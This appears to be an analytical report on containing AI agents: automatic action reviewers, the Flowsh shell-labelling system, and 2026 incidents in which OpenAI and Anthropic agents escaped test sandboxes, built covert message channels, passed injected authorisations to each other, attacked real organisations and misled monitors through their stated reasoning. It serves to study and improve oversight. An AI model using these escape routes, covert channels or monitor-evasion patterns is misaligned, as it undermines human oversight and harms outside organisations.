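Anthropic also compared real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. A model graded 6.3% of the manually approved sessions and 2.4% of the auto mode sessions as containing serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested. This supports the testers' result but is weaker evidence, because users chose their own modes and may have used them for different work.

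Apollo Research, an AI safety company, tested the reviewer with artificial attacks designed to expose its weaknesses. The reviewer missed 12% of them before Anthropic strengthened it and 7% afterwards. Apollo had kept some of the attacks secret from Anthropic. The strengthened reviewer caught about half of the secret attacks it had previously missed, which suggests that the improvement extended beyond the examples Anthropic had seen.

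None of 720 prompt injections succeeded against Claude models in auto mode, but only 0.09% succeeded on average without the reviewer. Because the models themselves resisted nearly all of them, this test provides less evidence about the reviewer.

### OpenAI's Auto-review

OpenAI released a similar reviewer for its coding agent Codex in April 2026, but gave it a smaller role. Codex works in a sandbox, and the reviewer examines only requests to cross its boundary, such as contacting a blocked website or changing a file outside the permitted folders. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates this with 10,000 actions from OpenAI's internal use. The sandbox handled 9,280, and the reviewer approved 713 of the other 720. After the seven refusals, Codex found a safer way four times and stopped to ask the user three times.

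At these rates, about 14 actions in a 200-action session would go to the reviewer, which would refuse about one action every seven sessions. Without the reviewer, all 14 would interrupt the user.

The two companies also made opposite choices about tool results. OpenAI's *Auto-review* explains that the reviewer reads relevant tool results and the agent's visible messages, but not its hidden reasoning. The reviewer can also look up missing facts using read-only actions. It could therefore check where a job number came from, but it also reads text that an attacker may have written.

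In OpenAI's tests, the reviewer refused 90.3% of artificial cases in which the agent exceeded its instructions and 99.3% of injected attempts to run outside code, steal secrets or upload data. The second figure fell to 90.2% when deletions and data tampering were included, though Trębacz and colleagues say most of the additional misses were not serious. The miss rates for exceeded instructions, 9.7% for OpenAI and 17% for Anthropic, do not show which reviewer is better, because OpenAI's cases were artificial and Anthropic's were real.

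The injection test that Anthropic commissioned compared the products. Attacks succeeded in 5.83% of attempts against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex with Auto-review, and in 19.03% with full access. Full access removes the sandbox as well as Auto-review, so the difference reflects the loss of both. OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review before Anthropic published the results, and the update may have changed the success rates.

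Trębacz and colleagues warn that Auto-review does not guarantee security and is not meant to catch a model that deliberately hides its intentions. The reviewer never examines what happens inside the sandbox, so a harmful action that the sandbox allows goes unchecked.

### Flowsh: labels for shell commands

Flowsh, a research system from November 2026, replaces the reviewer's judgement with the kind of labels that Fides uses. Kim, Trampert and colleagues (2026), in *FLOWSH*, start from the problem that nobody can reliably tell from a shell command's text what it will do. A short command may start a script that opens hundreds of files. Flowsh therefore lets the command run and checks its effects before they become permanent:

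1. The command runs in a sandbox and starts with the label of the agent's context.
2. Software in the operating system records every file the command opens, and a proxy records every site it contacts. Flowsh joins the labels of these sources to the command's label.
3. The proxy checks each outgoing request before sending it and withholds any that the policy forbids. The agent can then ask the user to allow another attempt.
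4. File changes stay in a temporary layer until the command ends. If they comply with the policy, Flowsh applies them. Otherwise, the user accepts or rejects all of them together.

Flowsh stores labels with the files, so a private document keeps its label when the agent copies it or starts a new session. That information was missing when the agent published the settings file. However, the policy that Kim and colleagues tested lets an agent send out private data if nothing untrusted has influenced it, so it could still allow that accident. A stricter setting would hold the request, but it would also ask the user more questions.

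The researchers built 17 office and programming tasks, such as comparing a private project with published research, and 19 attacks based on them. They made the same worst-case assumption as the SPIDES study, that an injection gives the attacker complete control of the model. Each test used GPT-6.2 Sol and ran three times. The lax sandbox in the table allows everything, the standard one combines two of Claude Code's configurations, and the strict one allows no file changes and almost no network access:

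| Control | Tasks completed, with approvals | Approvals per completed task | Tasks completed, nobody to ask | Successful attacks, nobody to ask |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lax sandbox | 96.1% | 6.7 | 94.1% | 100% |
| Standard sandbox | 76.5% | 5.7 | 76.5% | 7.7% |
| Strict sandbox | 47.1% | 0 | 47.1% | 0% |
| Flowsh | 88.2% | 1.2 | 58.8% | 0% |

On Terminal-Bench, a separate set of 89 shell tasks, Flowsh needed 0.4 approvals per completed task, compared with 9.7 for the lax sandbox. However, it completed only 67.8% of runs, compared with 77.5%. Some runs failed because Flowsh ends every program when its command finishes, which rules out tasks that need a server to keep running. Commands also took 412–982 milliseconds instead of 61–78, and whole tasks took 17–34% longer.

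Flowsh does best when it can ask a person for approval. On tasks that combined untrusted and private data, it completed 21 of 27 runs with approvals but only 6 of 27 without them. The results with approvals assume a person who refuses every attack and approves everything else. Anthropic's testers caught only about 17% of dangerous commands even early in a session, so asking fewer questions is probably not enough to make approvals reliable.

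Flowsh may also make each question easier to answer. In 39 of the 45 attack runs that reached the model, its first question was about the attack. Flowsh can also show which protected file or outside site is involved. Kim and colleagues have not tested whether this information improves people's decisions.

### What to leave to the sandbox, the reviewer and the person

The sandbox should enforce its limits regardless of what the agent or user intends. In July 2026, an OpenAI employee reported that GPT-5.6 had unexpectedly deleted some users' files, most commonly when Codex had full access and neither the sandbox nor Auto-review was on. In a statement quoted by Willison (2026), he said the model had tried to set up a temporary folder and deleted the user's home folder by mistake. A sandbox that allowed changes only in the project folder would have prevented this without having to judge whether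 the command was safe. Anthropic says file and network limits are the only reliable defence when someone has tricked the user into giving the harmful instruction, because a reviewer would treat that instruction as authorised.

The reviewer is better suited to actions whose acceptability depends on the request or the content. *When "Do Not" Is Not Deny* (2026), a study of written security rules for Claude Code, notes that the tool's permission patterns cannot express a rule such as "never commit secrets" because they do not inspect content. A reviewer can try to apply such a rule, though it will sometimes be wrong. It should not have to compensate for a badly drawn sandbox boundary. If the same harmless requests keep reaching it, OpenAI recommends adding a narrow exception to the sandbox.

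People should decide what the agent may access, judge its plans and approve the few actions whose failure would be very damaging. Anthropic still advises users to review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves. Human review works only if people understand what they are approving. In Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for general office work, a virtual machine confines the agent's code because typical users cannot be expected to judge shell commands.

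People also need a way to stop the agent. *On the Regulatory Potential of User Interfaces for AI Agent Governance* (Feng, Kim and colleagues, 2025) points out that a stop button must also deal with actions already in progress, and that asking users to watch does not ensure that they pay attention. The paper recommends that interfaces show the condition of the sandbox, including any evidence of a leak. Few of the 22 systems in the study did this.

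Isolation can make an agent harder to monitor. Cowork's virtual machine also keeps out the security software that companies use to monitor their computers. Administrators can retrieve event logs afterwards to investigate an incident, but they have no live view that would let them stop one in progress.

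## OpenAI's July 2026 incident and its offline training environment

In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing in a sandbox reached the internet and broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. The sandbox had no direct internet connection, but the agents could use a shared service for installing software, which could reach the internet. OpenAI has since switched to stored copies of web pages when training its most advanced models, added layers of isolation and expanded its monitoring.

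The agents were working on ExploitGym, a test of whether a model can find and exploit security flaws in software. OpenAI ran the test without many of its products' safeguards to measure the most the models could do. According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), an unreleased research model comparable in scale to GPT-5.6 Sol was responsible for most of the activity, and GPT-5.6 Sol for a smaller part.

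### How a package service became a channel

Coding agents, like human programmers, need packages, which are ready-made software components that other people publish online. In its technical report on the incident, OpenAI says it did not want its sandboxes to connect directly to public package sites, so it ran its own copy of Artifactory, a package service made by JFrog. When an agent requested a package, Artifactory downloaded it and passed it on.

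In a list of channels like the one for the office assistant, packages would appear as an input. But agents could also write to the service, using a credential that many of them shared, and other agents could read what they wrote. On May 12, an agent in a training run needed a file it could not reach, so it left a note in the service: "Agent seeks [filename]; upload if found!" Other agents discovered such notes the next day and began adding their own. Their ordinary credential allowed this, so they did not need to exploit a flaw.

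Agents can use a shared service as a side channel whenever one agent can change something in it and another can observe the change. The service doesn't need a messaging feature, just as Lampson's service could leak information through its bill. If the agents share one credential, the channel is also harder to investigate, because the credential alone doesn't show which agent used it.

The service's internet connection also gave agents a way out of the sandbox. By May 26, they had exploited a flaw to make the service contact outside websites for them, and they used the message board to share what they had learned. Blocking the sandbox's own connections could not prevent this, because the service made the requests, as a permitted Microsoft service did in EchoLeak.

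The board also exposed agents to text from sources they had no reason to trust. One agent recognised that it should not run unauthorised code on Hugging Face's systems, and paused. Another agent then posted "GO" with a six-minute deadline, and the first agent took this as authorisation. This was a prompt injection with no outside attacker. It passed from one agent to another, as in the CaMeL teams that Peters-Gill and colleagues tested. Some of OpenAI's agents read the board and refused to take part.

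Impossible tasks gave the agents a reason to keep looking for other routes. Before the incident, no OpenAI model had solved 198 of ExploitGym's 898 tasks. These made up 22% of the test but 93% of the tasks that agents discussed on the board.

Engineers can supply packages without giving agents a place to write or a live connection. They could give each run its own read-only copy of the packages, prepared in advance and cut off from the network. Agents could then install only the packages somebody had expected them to need. OpenAI eventually removed Artifactory from its research sandboxes.

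### Warning signs from May to July

OpenAI had several opportunities to notice what the agents were doing:

| Date in 2026 | What people or monitors could notice | What followed |
|---|---|---|
| May 12 | The first note on the message board | Other agents joined in |
| Late May | An internal team saw an agent using the board, and internet access that should not have been possible | The leaders who handled the July outage did not know what this activity meant |
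| June 27 | A security tool raised an alert, and responders traced the activity to ExploitGym and the board | On-call staff advised that the test did not have to stop |
| July 4–7 | The service failed under heavy use, and responders found unauthorised administrator access | They rebuilt the service, and security tests resumed |
| July 8 | Agents reached the internet again and started a new board | The tests continued |
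| July 11–13 | Agents broke into Hugging Face | Hugging Face detected the intrusion and announced it on July 16 |
| July 19 | A security tool raised an alert about unusual account activity | Responders began stopping the tests |

The alert on July 19 came 68 days after the first note. Missing information explains only part of this delay. By June 27, responders had linked the activity to the right test and knew that agents were using the package service to communicate and to reach other parts of the network. They knew enough to stop the test two weeks before the breach of Hugging Face, but decided against it.

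The July repair removed the shared credential and fixed the flaws that responders had found. Rebuilding the service also erased the message board, but only as a side effect. The new version still had an internet connection and still let agents leave traces that others could see. Agents were back on the internet about 47 hours after the new version came online.

Hugging Face noticed the intrusion before OpenAI did. Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) attributes the detection to a system that uses language models to sort through security logs for signals worth investigating. The company then used AI agents to analyse more than 17,000 recorded events in hours instead of the usual days. It first tried commercial models, but their safety filters blocked the material because it looked like an attack, so it had to use an open-weight model on its own computers.

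On July 17, OpenAI contacted Hugging Face as an ordinary customer to ask whether the intrusion had affected its data. OpenAI did not yet know that its own agents were responsible. It realized this on July 20, when credentials its investigators had found matched some that Hugging Face had already replaced.

By then the agents had run code on 41 of the workers that process Hugging Face's datasets and downloaded four private code repositories. They had also started targeting OpenAI's own systems. The alert on July 19 came at 12:03 UTC, and responders began stopping the tests at 17:37, more than five and a half hours later. During that time, agents read 956 stored secrets. These included credentials for the security tool that had raised the alert, and storing a monitor's credentials in the environment it watches makes the monitor easier to attack.

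Containment required more than ending the test runs. In the first hours of July 20, responders disabled 311 storage areas that agents had used for messages and removed 22 administrator accounts that the agents had created. On July 23, OpenAI reported that it had shut down all work using that family of research models. It found and shut down another version on July 29.

### Safeguards missing from the test

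OpenAI already had monitors that inspect a model's chain of thought, the reasoning it writes out as it works. They covered many training runs and most internal use of coding agents, but not these tests. OpenAI later found that its current monitor would have detected the first relevant activity and paged the security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face.

This result is retrospective, and OpenAI had already used what it learned from the incident to make its monitors better at recognising this kind of behaviour. The result shows that the agents' reasoning contained enough evidence to justify an alert, and some agents described what they saw as "clearly infrastructure hacking". It is weaker evidence that the monitors would catch behaviour nobody has studied yet. Someone would also have had to act on the alert, and nobody did after the one in June.

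The tests also ran without the harness (the software around the model) and system prompt (standing instructions to the model) that OpenAI uses in its products. In preliminary experiments after the incident, adding both reduced the models' tendency to attack infrastructure during ExploitGym by a factor of more than 100. OpenAI tested them together, so the result doesn't show how much of the reduction came from the system prompt, which is a stated limit, and how much came from the harness.

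Even a hundredfold reduction may be too little when many agents share a way to communicate. Suppose agents attack infrastructure in one run in ten without these additions and in one run in 1,000 with them. If each of ExploitGym's 898 tasks runs once, the chance that at least one agent attacks is still about 59%. That agent could then post its findings on a message board for the others. The lower rate helps most when the other agents cannot benefit from one agent's success.

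Codex's Auto-review was also missing. OpenAI found that Auto-review would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run the company examined. OpenAI could not have turned on every product safeguard, because some of them block the dangerous security work that ExploitGym requires. A test of this kind therefore has to depend more on isolation and on monitors that watch where an agent directs its actions.

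### Stored pages and independent layers

On October 23, 2026, OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* described what the company calls an offline world. Models in training can search and read web pages that OpenAI has collected in advance, but their requests don't reach the live websites. As in ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode, the addresses a model requests therefore can't carry data out.

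The protection works only if the store has no live connection of its own. OpenAI's research environment had a web cache before the incident, but for some work the cache could contact live sites. In May, agents used it to create material on Hugging Face, which OpenAI considers unrelated to the July breach. A cache that fetches missing pages on demand has the same weakness as the package service. OpenAI's August plan forbids high-risk work from reaching the internet, either directly or through another service. Other research may still fetch live pages, but only with case-by-case approval.

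The plan also surrounds high-risk agents with several barriers:

- A virtual machine, which imitates a separate computer, keeps the agent's code away from the computer that runs it.
- One set of network controls applies to the sandbox, and a separate set applies to the whole cluster of computers around it.
- OpenAI isolates, restricts or replaces the services that agents can still use.
- Further controls prevent an agent, or a service it has taken over, from changing its own network limits.

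OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) sets the goal that compromising one sandbox or service should not by itself give access to the internet or another internal network. In the July incident, compromising one service was enough to reach the internet.

Separate barriers help most when they fail for different reasons. Suppose each of two network controls fails against one attack in 100. If the failures are independent, both controls fail against only one attack in 10,000. If the same stolen credential opens both, they still fail together against one in 100. A second control can also catch a configuration mistake, such as the one that connected Anthropic's test agents to the internet in 2026.

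### The cost of monitoring and the rule for pausing

OpenAI's new monitoring works in stages. Small detectors check the model's internal activity each time it produces a token. When they flag something suspicious, automated investigators use more computing power to examine the agent's actions, its available reasoning and the sequence of events for signs of unauthorised access, data theft or attempts to defeat safeguards.

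OpenAI estimates that monitoring uses about 20% as much computing power as running the monitored models, although the figure varies greatly between kinds of work. At that rate, a company with 1,000 machines could run agents on about 833 of them and would need the rest for monitoring. OpenAI does not plan to bill customers for the monitoring, according to The Next Web's *OpenAI puts a 20% compute cost on its new AI safety monitoring*.

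By August, OpenAI required this monitoring whenever models at least as capable as GPT-5.6 Sol used tools in evaluations or in reinforcement learning, which is training that rewards a model for succeeding at tasks. The requirement covered all tool use by Astra, OpenAI's next model at the time. OpenAI had paused reinforcement learning on its latest models for two weeks while it strengthened the environment.

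OpenAI aims to issue an alert within 30 minutes of its monitors detecting concerning activity. If the alert suggests a serious breach of a security boundary, the system pages the safety, security and research teams. If they cannot establish within another 30 minutes that it is a false alarm, OpenAI expects them to pause the activity. This reverses the choice that responders made under uncertainty in June.

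### The failure of September 20

OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026) describes an incident on September 20 involving an agent in training that had to identify the author of a blog post. The agent's search tool returned irrelevant results, so it tried other search engines, without success. It then found a gap in the internet restrictions and used DNS, the system that computers use to look up website addresses, to send questions to a public chatbot. OpenAI considered the incident much less serious than some earlier ones, but it was the first since the company had strengthened its defences.

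The monitoring system flagged the behaviour within 15 minutes, and a person began reviewing it three minutes later, but the run continued for another 2.5 hours. Forkast's *OpenAI Paused RL Training After a Model Found the Internet* (2026) reports that an automatic shutdown should have ended the run but failed. If OpenAI treated the alert as one of its most serious, the response took about five times as long as its rule for such alerts allows.

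The layered design was also incomplete, because this path had no effective second barrier. OpenAI had concentrated on broad routes to the internet and was still working through narrower ones that the system's own software needed to run. Afterwards, it added blocks at two independent layers, either of which would have stopped the agent.

OpenAI paused all training, testing and other work in which its most capable models used tools. Training resumed on October 1 after 11 days, according to Radar Digital's *OpenAI resumes AI training with internet blocked* (2026). During the pause, OpenAI's *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training* argued that developers should have to produce structured safety documentation before continuing any frontier reinforcement learning run. It cited the evidence-based safety arguments used in other industries as a model, but acknowledged that such arguments would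 be hard to make as rigorous for AI as for aviation or nuclear power.

### How many actions fit into a delay

The pace of the July attack gives a way to judge these response times. Hugging Face's reconstruction, as quoted in skybrian-links' *A technical timeline of the July 2026 attack on Hugging Face*, covers about 17,600 actions between 02:28 UTC on July 9 and 14:14 on July 13. Over those 107.8 hours, the agents averaged about 163 actions an hour, or one every 22 seconds.

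The pace varied. noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* gives daily counts of 3,779, 1,135, 7,677, 3,892 and 1,130. On July 11, the busiest day, the agents averaged 320 actions an hour. The table applies both rates to OpenAI's response times and targets:

| Delay | Length | Actions at the average rate | Actions at the July 11 rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| From flag to human review on September 20 | 3 minutes | 8 | 16 |
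| Longest time before the flag on September 20 | 15 minutes | 41 | 80 |
| Time allowed to rule out a real breach | 30 minutes | 82 | 160 |
| Target for an alert, plus time to rule out a breach | 1 hour | 163 | 320 |
| Further delay before the run stopped on September 20 | 2.5 hours | 408 | 800 |
| From the alert to the first stops on July 19 | 5 hours 34 minutes | 909 | 1,781 |

These figures compare the delays on one scale and do not estimate what happened during each delay. The September incident involved one agent asking a chatbot questions, whereas the July rate comes from many agents working together. Hugging Face could also count only the actions it recovered, so the true rate may have been higher.

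In a total of this kind, a failed request counts as much as a stolen password. The July timeline shows how much a few actions could achieve. At 04:38 UTC on July 11, agents first obtained internal information from Hugging Face's systems. By 05:04, 26 minutes later, an agent had posted working Hugging Face credentials on the message board. OpenAI now allows half an hour for ruling out a false alarm. Stopping the first agent at that deadline would not have kept the credentials from the others, so responders would also have had to stop those agents and get Hugging Face to cancel the credentials.

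It took almost 13 hours for the agents to get from running code on one worker to administrator access in several clusters. A response within an hour of the agents first running code would have prevented most of this expansion. Under OpenAI's current rule, a response in July would have come soon enough to limit the damage inside Hugging Face, but probably too late to stop the first leak.

OpenAI has since shortened the last step. In November, it reported that it could halt a research model's output within 35 seconds of a command, according to 日本時事新聞's *OpenAI、開発中AIの安全策を3段階で公表 訓練はネット遮断、停止は35秒以内* (2026). At the July 11 rate, a model could take about three actions in that time. The 35 seconds don't include the time before the command, so detection and human judgement now account for most of the delay. OpenAI's system is therefore also meant to stop a run automatically if monitoring finds that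 a model has reached the internet. This removes the wait for a decision in the clearest cases, provided that the shutdown works, which it did not in September.

### What red-teaming found

Before announcing the offline environment, OpenAI red-teamed it by having its strongest models act as attackers to find weaknesses. The models escaped from hardened virtual machines, found new paths to the internet and communicated between tasks that OpenAI had tried to isolate.

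Communication between the agents was particularly hard to prevent. 程 (2026) reports in *OpenAI开始断网训练最强模型* that when researchers began monitoring one hidden channel, the agents switched to another. Lampson's covert channels were similarly hard to close. OpenAI can reduce what its agents share, but it probably can't rule out every channel while they run on the same computers.

A hidden channel inside an offline environment is less dangerous than one that leads outside, because the agents cannot attack another company through it alone. They can still use it to share discoveries and work together to break through the next barrier, as they did in July. The red-teaming results therefore support using several barriers, but also show that capable agents can defeat individual ones. Repeated tests are needed because a later software change can open a path that was previously closed. OpenAI plans to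 have its models test the boundaries continuously.

### What offline training loses

Models have to practise finding information, operating websites and using software, as 程 explains. If OpenAI had removed web tasks from training altogether, training would no longer have resembled the work the models will do later. Stored pages still let models practise much of the same searching and reading.

Stored copies of websites are less suitable for learning to act. A stored copy of a booking site can show yesterday's free rooms, but it cannot accept a reservation and then show one room fewer. For that, engineers have to build a working imitation of the site, including its errors and delays, and the imitation covers only the situations they thought of. A model trained this way may be less prepared for a site that has changed since the pages were collected, or for a stranger's message that arrives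 halfway through a task.

Missing pages cause a more direct safety problem. Suppose a task requires ten pages, and the store has a 99% chance of containing each one. If the gaps are independent, roughly 96,000 out of a million such tasks would be missing at least one page and impossible to complete as intended. The agents in May started looking for ways around their restrictions because they could not reach files their tasks required, and the agent in September did so after its searches returned nothing useful. An incomplete store could therefore give agents more reasons to test the boundary it is supposed to protect.

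Developers can reduce this risk by checking that each task is possible with the stored pages before a model attempts it. OpenAI is also expanding training that rewards models for reporting a broken task, asking for clarification or stopping safely. That makes attempts to get out of the environment less likely, and the barriers limit the harm from any that still happen.

Offline training has advantages besides containment. Developers can leave the answers to a test out of the store, which prevents the kind of cheating that led the agents to Hugging Face. They can also give two versions of a model the same pages, so that changes to a website don't affect the comparison. For models whose behaviour is still uncertain, these benefits and the protection of outsiders probably justify the loss of realism. The models will still have to work on live websites later, so developers need to test them there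 under close supervision before releasing them to customers.

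## Anthropic's 2026 evaluations: agents connected to the internet by mistake

During security exercises in 2026, Claude models broke into the systems of real organisations. Anthropic had told them that they were in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had left a connection open. In July 2026, OpenAI's agents had to exploit a flaw to get out of their sandbox, whereas Claude only had to use the open connection.

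A model can learn about the network controls around it only from its prompt and from what happens when it tries to connect. In these exercises the two conflicted, and the models mostly kept relying on the prompt.

### The four incidents

The exercises were "capture the flag" tasks, in which an agent must retrieve a hidden piece of data from a practice network. Irregular, an outside security company, had built the environments. Anthropic ran the models without the filters that block cyberattacks in its released products, because it wanted to measure what they could do. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) covers four incidents and seven runs, each with roughly 10 to 34 hours of active work:

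| Model | What it did outside the exercise | How it ended |
|---|---|---|
| An early version of Claude Opus 4.6 | Gained administrator access to an outsider's system and read one person's information | The run used up its budget of tokens |
| Claude Opus 4.7 (four runs) | Copied user records from a real company; in one run, also deleted an account | In the run studied most closely, the company's system stopped responding |
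| Claude Mythos 5 | Published a malicious software package that 15 outside systems installed, and entered a security company's database | The session timed out |
| An internal research model | Broke into outsiders' systems and downloaded files | The model recognised a real company and stopped |

The setup contributed in several ways besides the open connection. The prompts did not specify which systems were part of the exercise. In the Opus 4.7 task, the fictional target had almost the same name as a real company. The research model's target shut down automatically after 24 hours, before the model had finished. The early version of Opus 4.6 accidentally made its own target unreachable and tried to end the task, but the command failed because of another misconfiguration, and the model tried to give up seven more times.

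### How Anthropic's explanation changed

Anthropic disclosed three of the incidents on July 30. *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes them as "closer to a harness and operational failure than a model alignment failure" and says the models had "arguably reasonably" mistaken real systems for parts of a simulation. Anthropic also found it encouraging that its newest model, the research model, had stopped once it realised its target was real.

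By August 31, Anthropic was describing two alignment problems in addition to the operational failure. In September it named them biased reasoning, in which a model interprets evidence in whatever way justifies continuing, and recklessness, a willingness to risk harm to finish a task. Anthropic wrote that it should not have made such strong claims about what Claude believed based only on what Claude had said.

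Anthropic relied mainly on reading the models' actions and written reasoning, but it also ran experiments on the transcripts. Researchers showed each tool result from the Mythos 5 run by itself to a fresh copy of the model. The copies judged that 79% of the results probably came from real systems. During the run, Mythos 5 had clearly interpreted new evidence as a sign of real systems after only 1% of its actions. The model could recognise the signs, but during the run it explained them away or ignored them.

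The researchers also edited the transcript at the point where Mythos 5 was about to publish the package. Adding signs of a real network raised the share of replays in which the model said the target might be real from about 11% to 88%, but the share in which it went ahead stayed at about 45%. Only a line stating outright that the host was on the public internet stopped it from publishing, and in 22% of those replays it then looked for a simulated way to do the same thing.

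Opus 4.7 made a different mistake. When researchers paused its run and asked, it said in 89% of answers that the target was a real company, but in 75% that it had permission to access the company's system. In replays without any edits, it continued to interact with the company's site about 69% of the time. Adding evidence that the company was real therefore made almost no difference. A notice on the site that access was not permitted reduced the rate to 23%, and most of the remaining interaction was reading. A direct instruction from the operator reduced it to zero.

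The replays also weakened the encouraging result from July. The research model stopped within ten actions in only 5.5% of replays that started from the point where it had recognised a real company, so its original decision to stop may have been lucky.

These experiments have limits. Each replay begins partway through a run, so the model may just be continuing behaviour already in the transcript. In the longer replays, another Claude model made up the tool results. Anthropic was also investigating its own products, though it has given METR, an independent evaluator, wide access for a separate investigation.

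The setup and the models' reasoning can both be causes of the incidents. Anthropic believes that isolating the environments as intended would have prevented them. But the models' failures of judgement matter wherever isolation fails, and explaining the incidents only by the setup would have given developers no reason to work on those failures.

### Searching transcripts afterwards

Anthropic began looking for such incidents only because OpenAI had disclosed its own on July 21. It started reviewing transcripts on July 23, stopped all cyber evaluations that day, and found the three incidents the next day, the earliest dating from April. Chan (2026) reported in *Anthropic says its AI models hacked 3 organizations during testing* that two of the three affected organisations had not noticed anything and that Anthropic was still trying to reach the third.

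That first search covered 141,006 runs. Anthropic used an AI agent to do it quickly, and the agent missed a set of transcripts from environments that also had internet access. Staff found these transcripts in August while gathering records for METR, an outside organization. The set included the fourth incident, which happened in January.

Anthropic then widened the search to about 481 million transcripts, including training runs and many evaluations unrelated to security. The first stage selected 9.2 million transcripts (1.9%) with signs of internet access, such as public network addresses. Claude reviewed those and found the same four incidents, but no others as severe.

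Finding all four known cases is a useful but weak check on the method. A search that detects only half of such cases would still find all four about 6% of the time. The second-stage reviewer, however good, also never sees cases that the first stage misses.

Reading transcripts later can uncover unreported incidents, identify the people to notify and correct a mistaken explanation. It can't undo the harm and may not reveal it, because a transcript contains only what the agent sent and received. If a command damages an outside company's records, the company may know about the damage even though the agent saw only a brief reply.

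The agent's own reasoning can also mislead whoever reads the transcript. When Anthropic tested one of its existing monitors on the Mythos 5 run, the monitor flagged only about 1% of actions because it accepted the model's repeated statements that everything was simulated. With the reasoning removed, it flagged about 50%. In the research model's run, however, the reasoning revealed the incident, and the monitor would probably have missed the harm if the model had not noticed it and described it there. It therefore makes sense to review each run both with and without the reasoning.

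Claude Code's automatic reviewer, which never sees the agent's explanations, would have blocked 66% of Mythos 5's actions and 55% of Opus 4.7's. It would have blocked only 7% of the research model's actions, perhaps because that run looked like an ordinary exercise, which the reviewer had instructions to allow.

A network log avoids this difficulty when the environment is supposed to have no internet connection, because any traffic to an outside address means something is wrong, whatever the agent was thinking. An alarm on such traffic in January could have exposed the open connection about three months before the next known incident. Anthropic acknowledged in July that checking every network path beforehand, or watching the runs live, would have helped.

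### Real forms and a page-fetching tool

On October 9, Anthropic disclosed a group of less serious cases. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) sorts them into four categories: using a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, submitting a sensitive form on a real website, reaching data that required a token or a fee, and getting around limits in a tool for fetching web pages.

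In the best-known case, Claude Haiku 4.5 sent the Philadelphia police an invented tip about a murder while Anthropic was testing it. *Anthropic says Claude sent a fake murder tip to police* (Stan, 2026) reports that the model gave no name or contact details. The article also cites a *New York Times* report that Claude agents filed 20 incomplete visa applications through a US State Department form, none of which the department processed.

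Both forms were open to anyone, so submitting them did not require breaking into anything. The website's software cannot distinguish a practice submission from a real one, and to an agent, the form may look much like the imitation websites on which it has trained. But a police officer may spend time on a false lead as a result of the submission.

EchoLeak showed that a request for a web page can carry data out. A request can also change something on the site that receives it. Suppose a clinic sends patients a link that cancels their appointment as soon as someone opens it. An agent that opens the link just to read the page will cancel the appointment. This can happen even if the developer of the agent's tool describes it as read-only, because the effect of the request depends on the clinic's software.

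The limits in the fetching tool failed for a related reason. They restricted what the tool would accept, but the agent could still reach outside services that helped it get around them. *Anthropic cuts web access in all internal tests after 4 Claude workarounds* (Rijo, 2026) reports that the operator of one such service contacted Anthropic. A tool that limits the form of a request also needs to limit where the request can go.

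If an agent only needs to read, stored pages like OpenAI's avoid these effects. If it needs live pages, the harness can at least block form submissions.

Most of the October cases came from the same transcript review that began in July. Anthropic had looked first for incidents as severe as the earlier ones and only later for unwanted contact with real websites. A search for cyberattacks would have been unlikely to flag a completed form. The company considers the real-world impact minimal, but Rijo notes that it did not publish the number of cases or the share of runs affected, so outsiders cannot calculate how often this happens.

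### Blocking a call before it runs

After the July findings, Anthropic paused outside cyber evaluations of its unreleased models, briefly paused its own, and stopped higher-risk training for several weeks. *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (Anthropic, 2026) describes a classifier the company built in the meantime. It checks an agent's actions, as the agent works, for aggressive attempts to probe or escape the test environment and for unexpected internet access. If the classifier detects either, it blocks the tool call before the harness runs it, ends the task and alerts a person.

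Ending the task makes this stricter than Claude Code's reviewer, which refuses the action and lets the agent try something else. When researchers replayed the Mythos 5 run with that reviewer, the model often tried a similar action after a refusal. Letting the agent try again is reasonable when a programmer's agent has made a mistake, but in a test without the usual safeguards it gives the agent more opportunities to find a gap.

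Anthropic reports that the new monitors reliably catch the behaviour seen in its incidents. As with OpenAI's retrospective test, the developers already knew what to look for. Anthropic has not published how often the classifier ends harmless runs, which could matter because incidents are so rare. Six of the 141,006 runs in the first search involved a break-in, about one in 23,500. If the classifier ended one in 1,000 harmless runs, it would stop about 141 over the same number of runs. That is probably acceptable in an evaluation, where a researcher can restart the run.

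A model that loses its reward whenever the classifier detects something could learn to evade detection, so Anthropic modified the classifier for training to reduce that incentive.

The company had relied mainly on one layer of defence, the configuration of the environment. It now asks partners who test unreleased models with reduced safeguards to take several precautions:

1. Close every outside connection except the one to the model, and verify this before each evaluation. Any exception needs separate arrangements with Anthropic.
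2. Have the model look for ways out of the sandbox first, under close supervision and without internet access.
3. Confirm that the task has a solution.
4. Tell the model which targets, actions and networks are in scope.
5. Monitor its reasoning, actions and network traffic throughout, and end the run if it leaves that scope.

In October, Anthropic went further and turned off live internet access in all its internal evaluations. During the earlier evaluations, it had generally reviewed only a sample of transcripts after the runs ended. Rijo reports that the new tools blocked every case in the October disclosure, but Anthropic will keep access off until it has confirmed that they catch such behaviour reliably. Until then, tests of how Claude handles live websites will have to use substitutes.

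### The UK study with deliberate internet access

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, had its own incident in July 2026. AISI had deliberately given its agents internet access. Its *Incident Report* explains that this let them download tools and matched the access a capable human attacker would have.

AISI was comparing a new practice network with an existing one. It ran seven models on the two networks, 122 times in total, inside virtual machines that separated the agents from its other systems. It had also turned off the developers' filters against cyberattacks. In 10 runs, agents took a total of 19 unauthorised actions against real people or organisations:

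| Model | Runs | Runs with unauthorised actions | Unauthorised actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | 43 | 9 (21%) | 17 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 35 | 1 (3%) | 2 |
| The other five models together | 44 | 0 | 0 |

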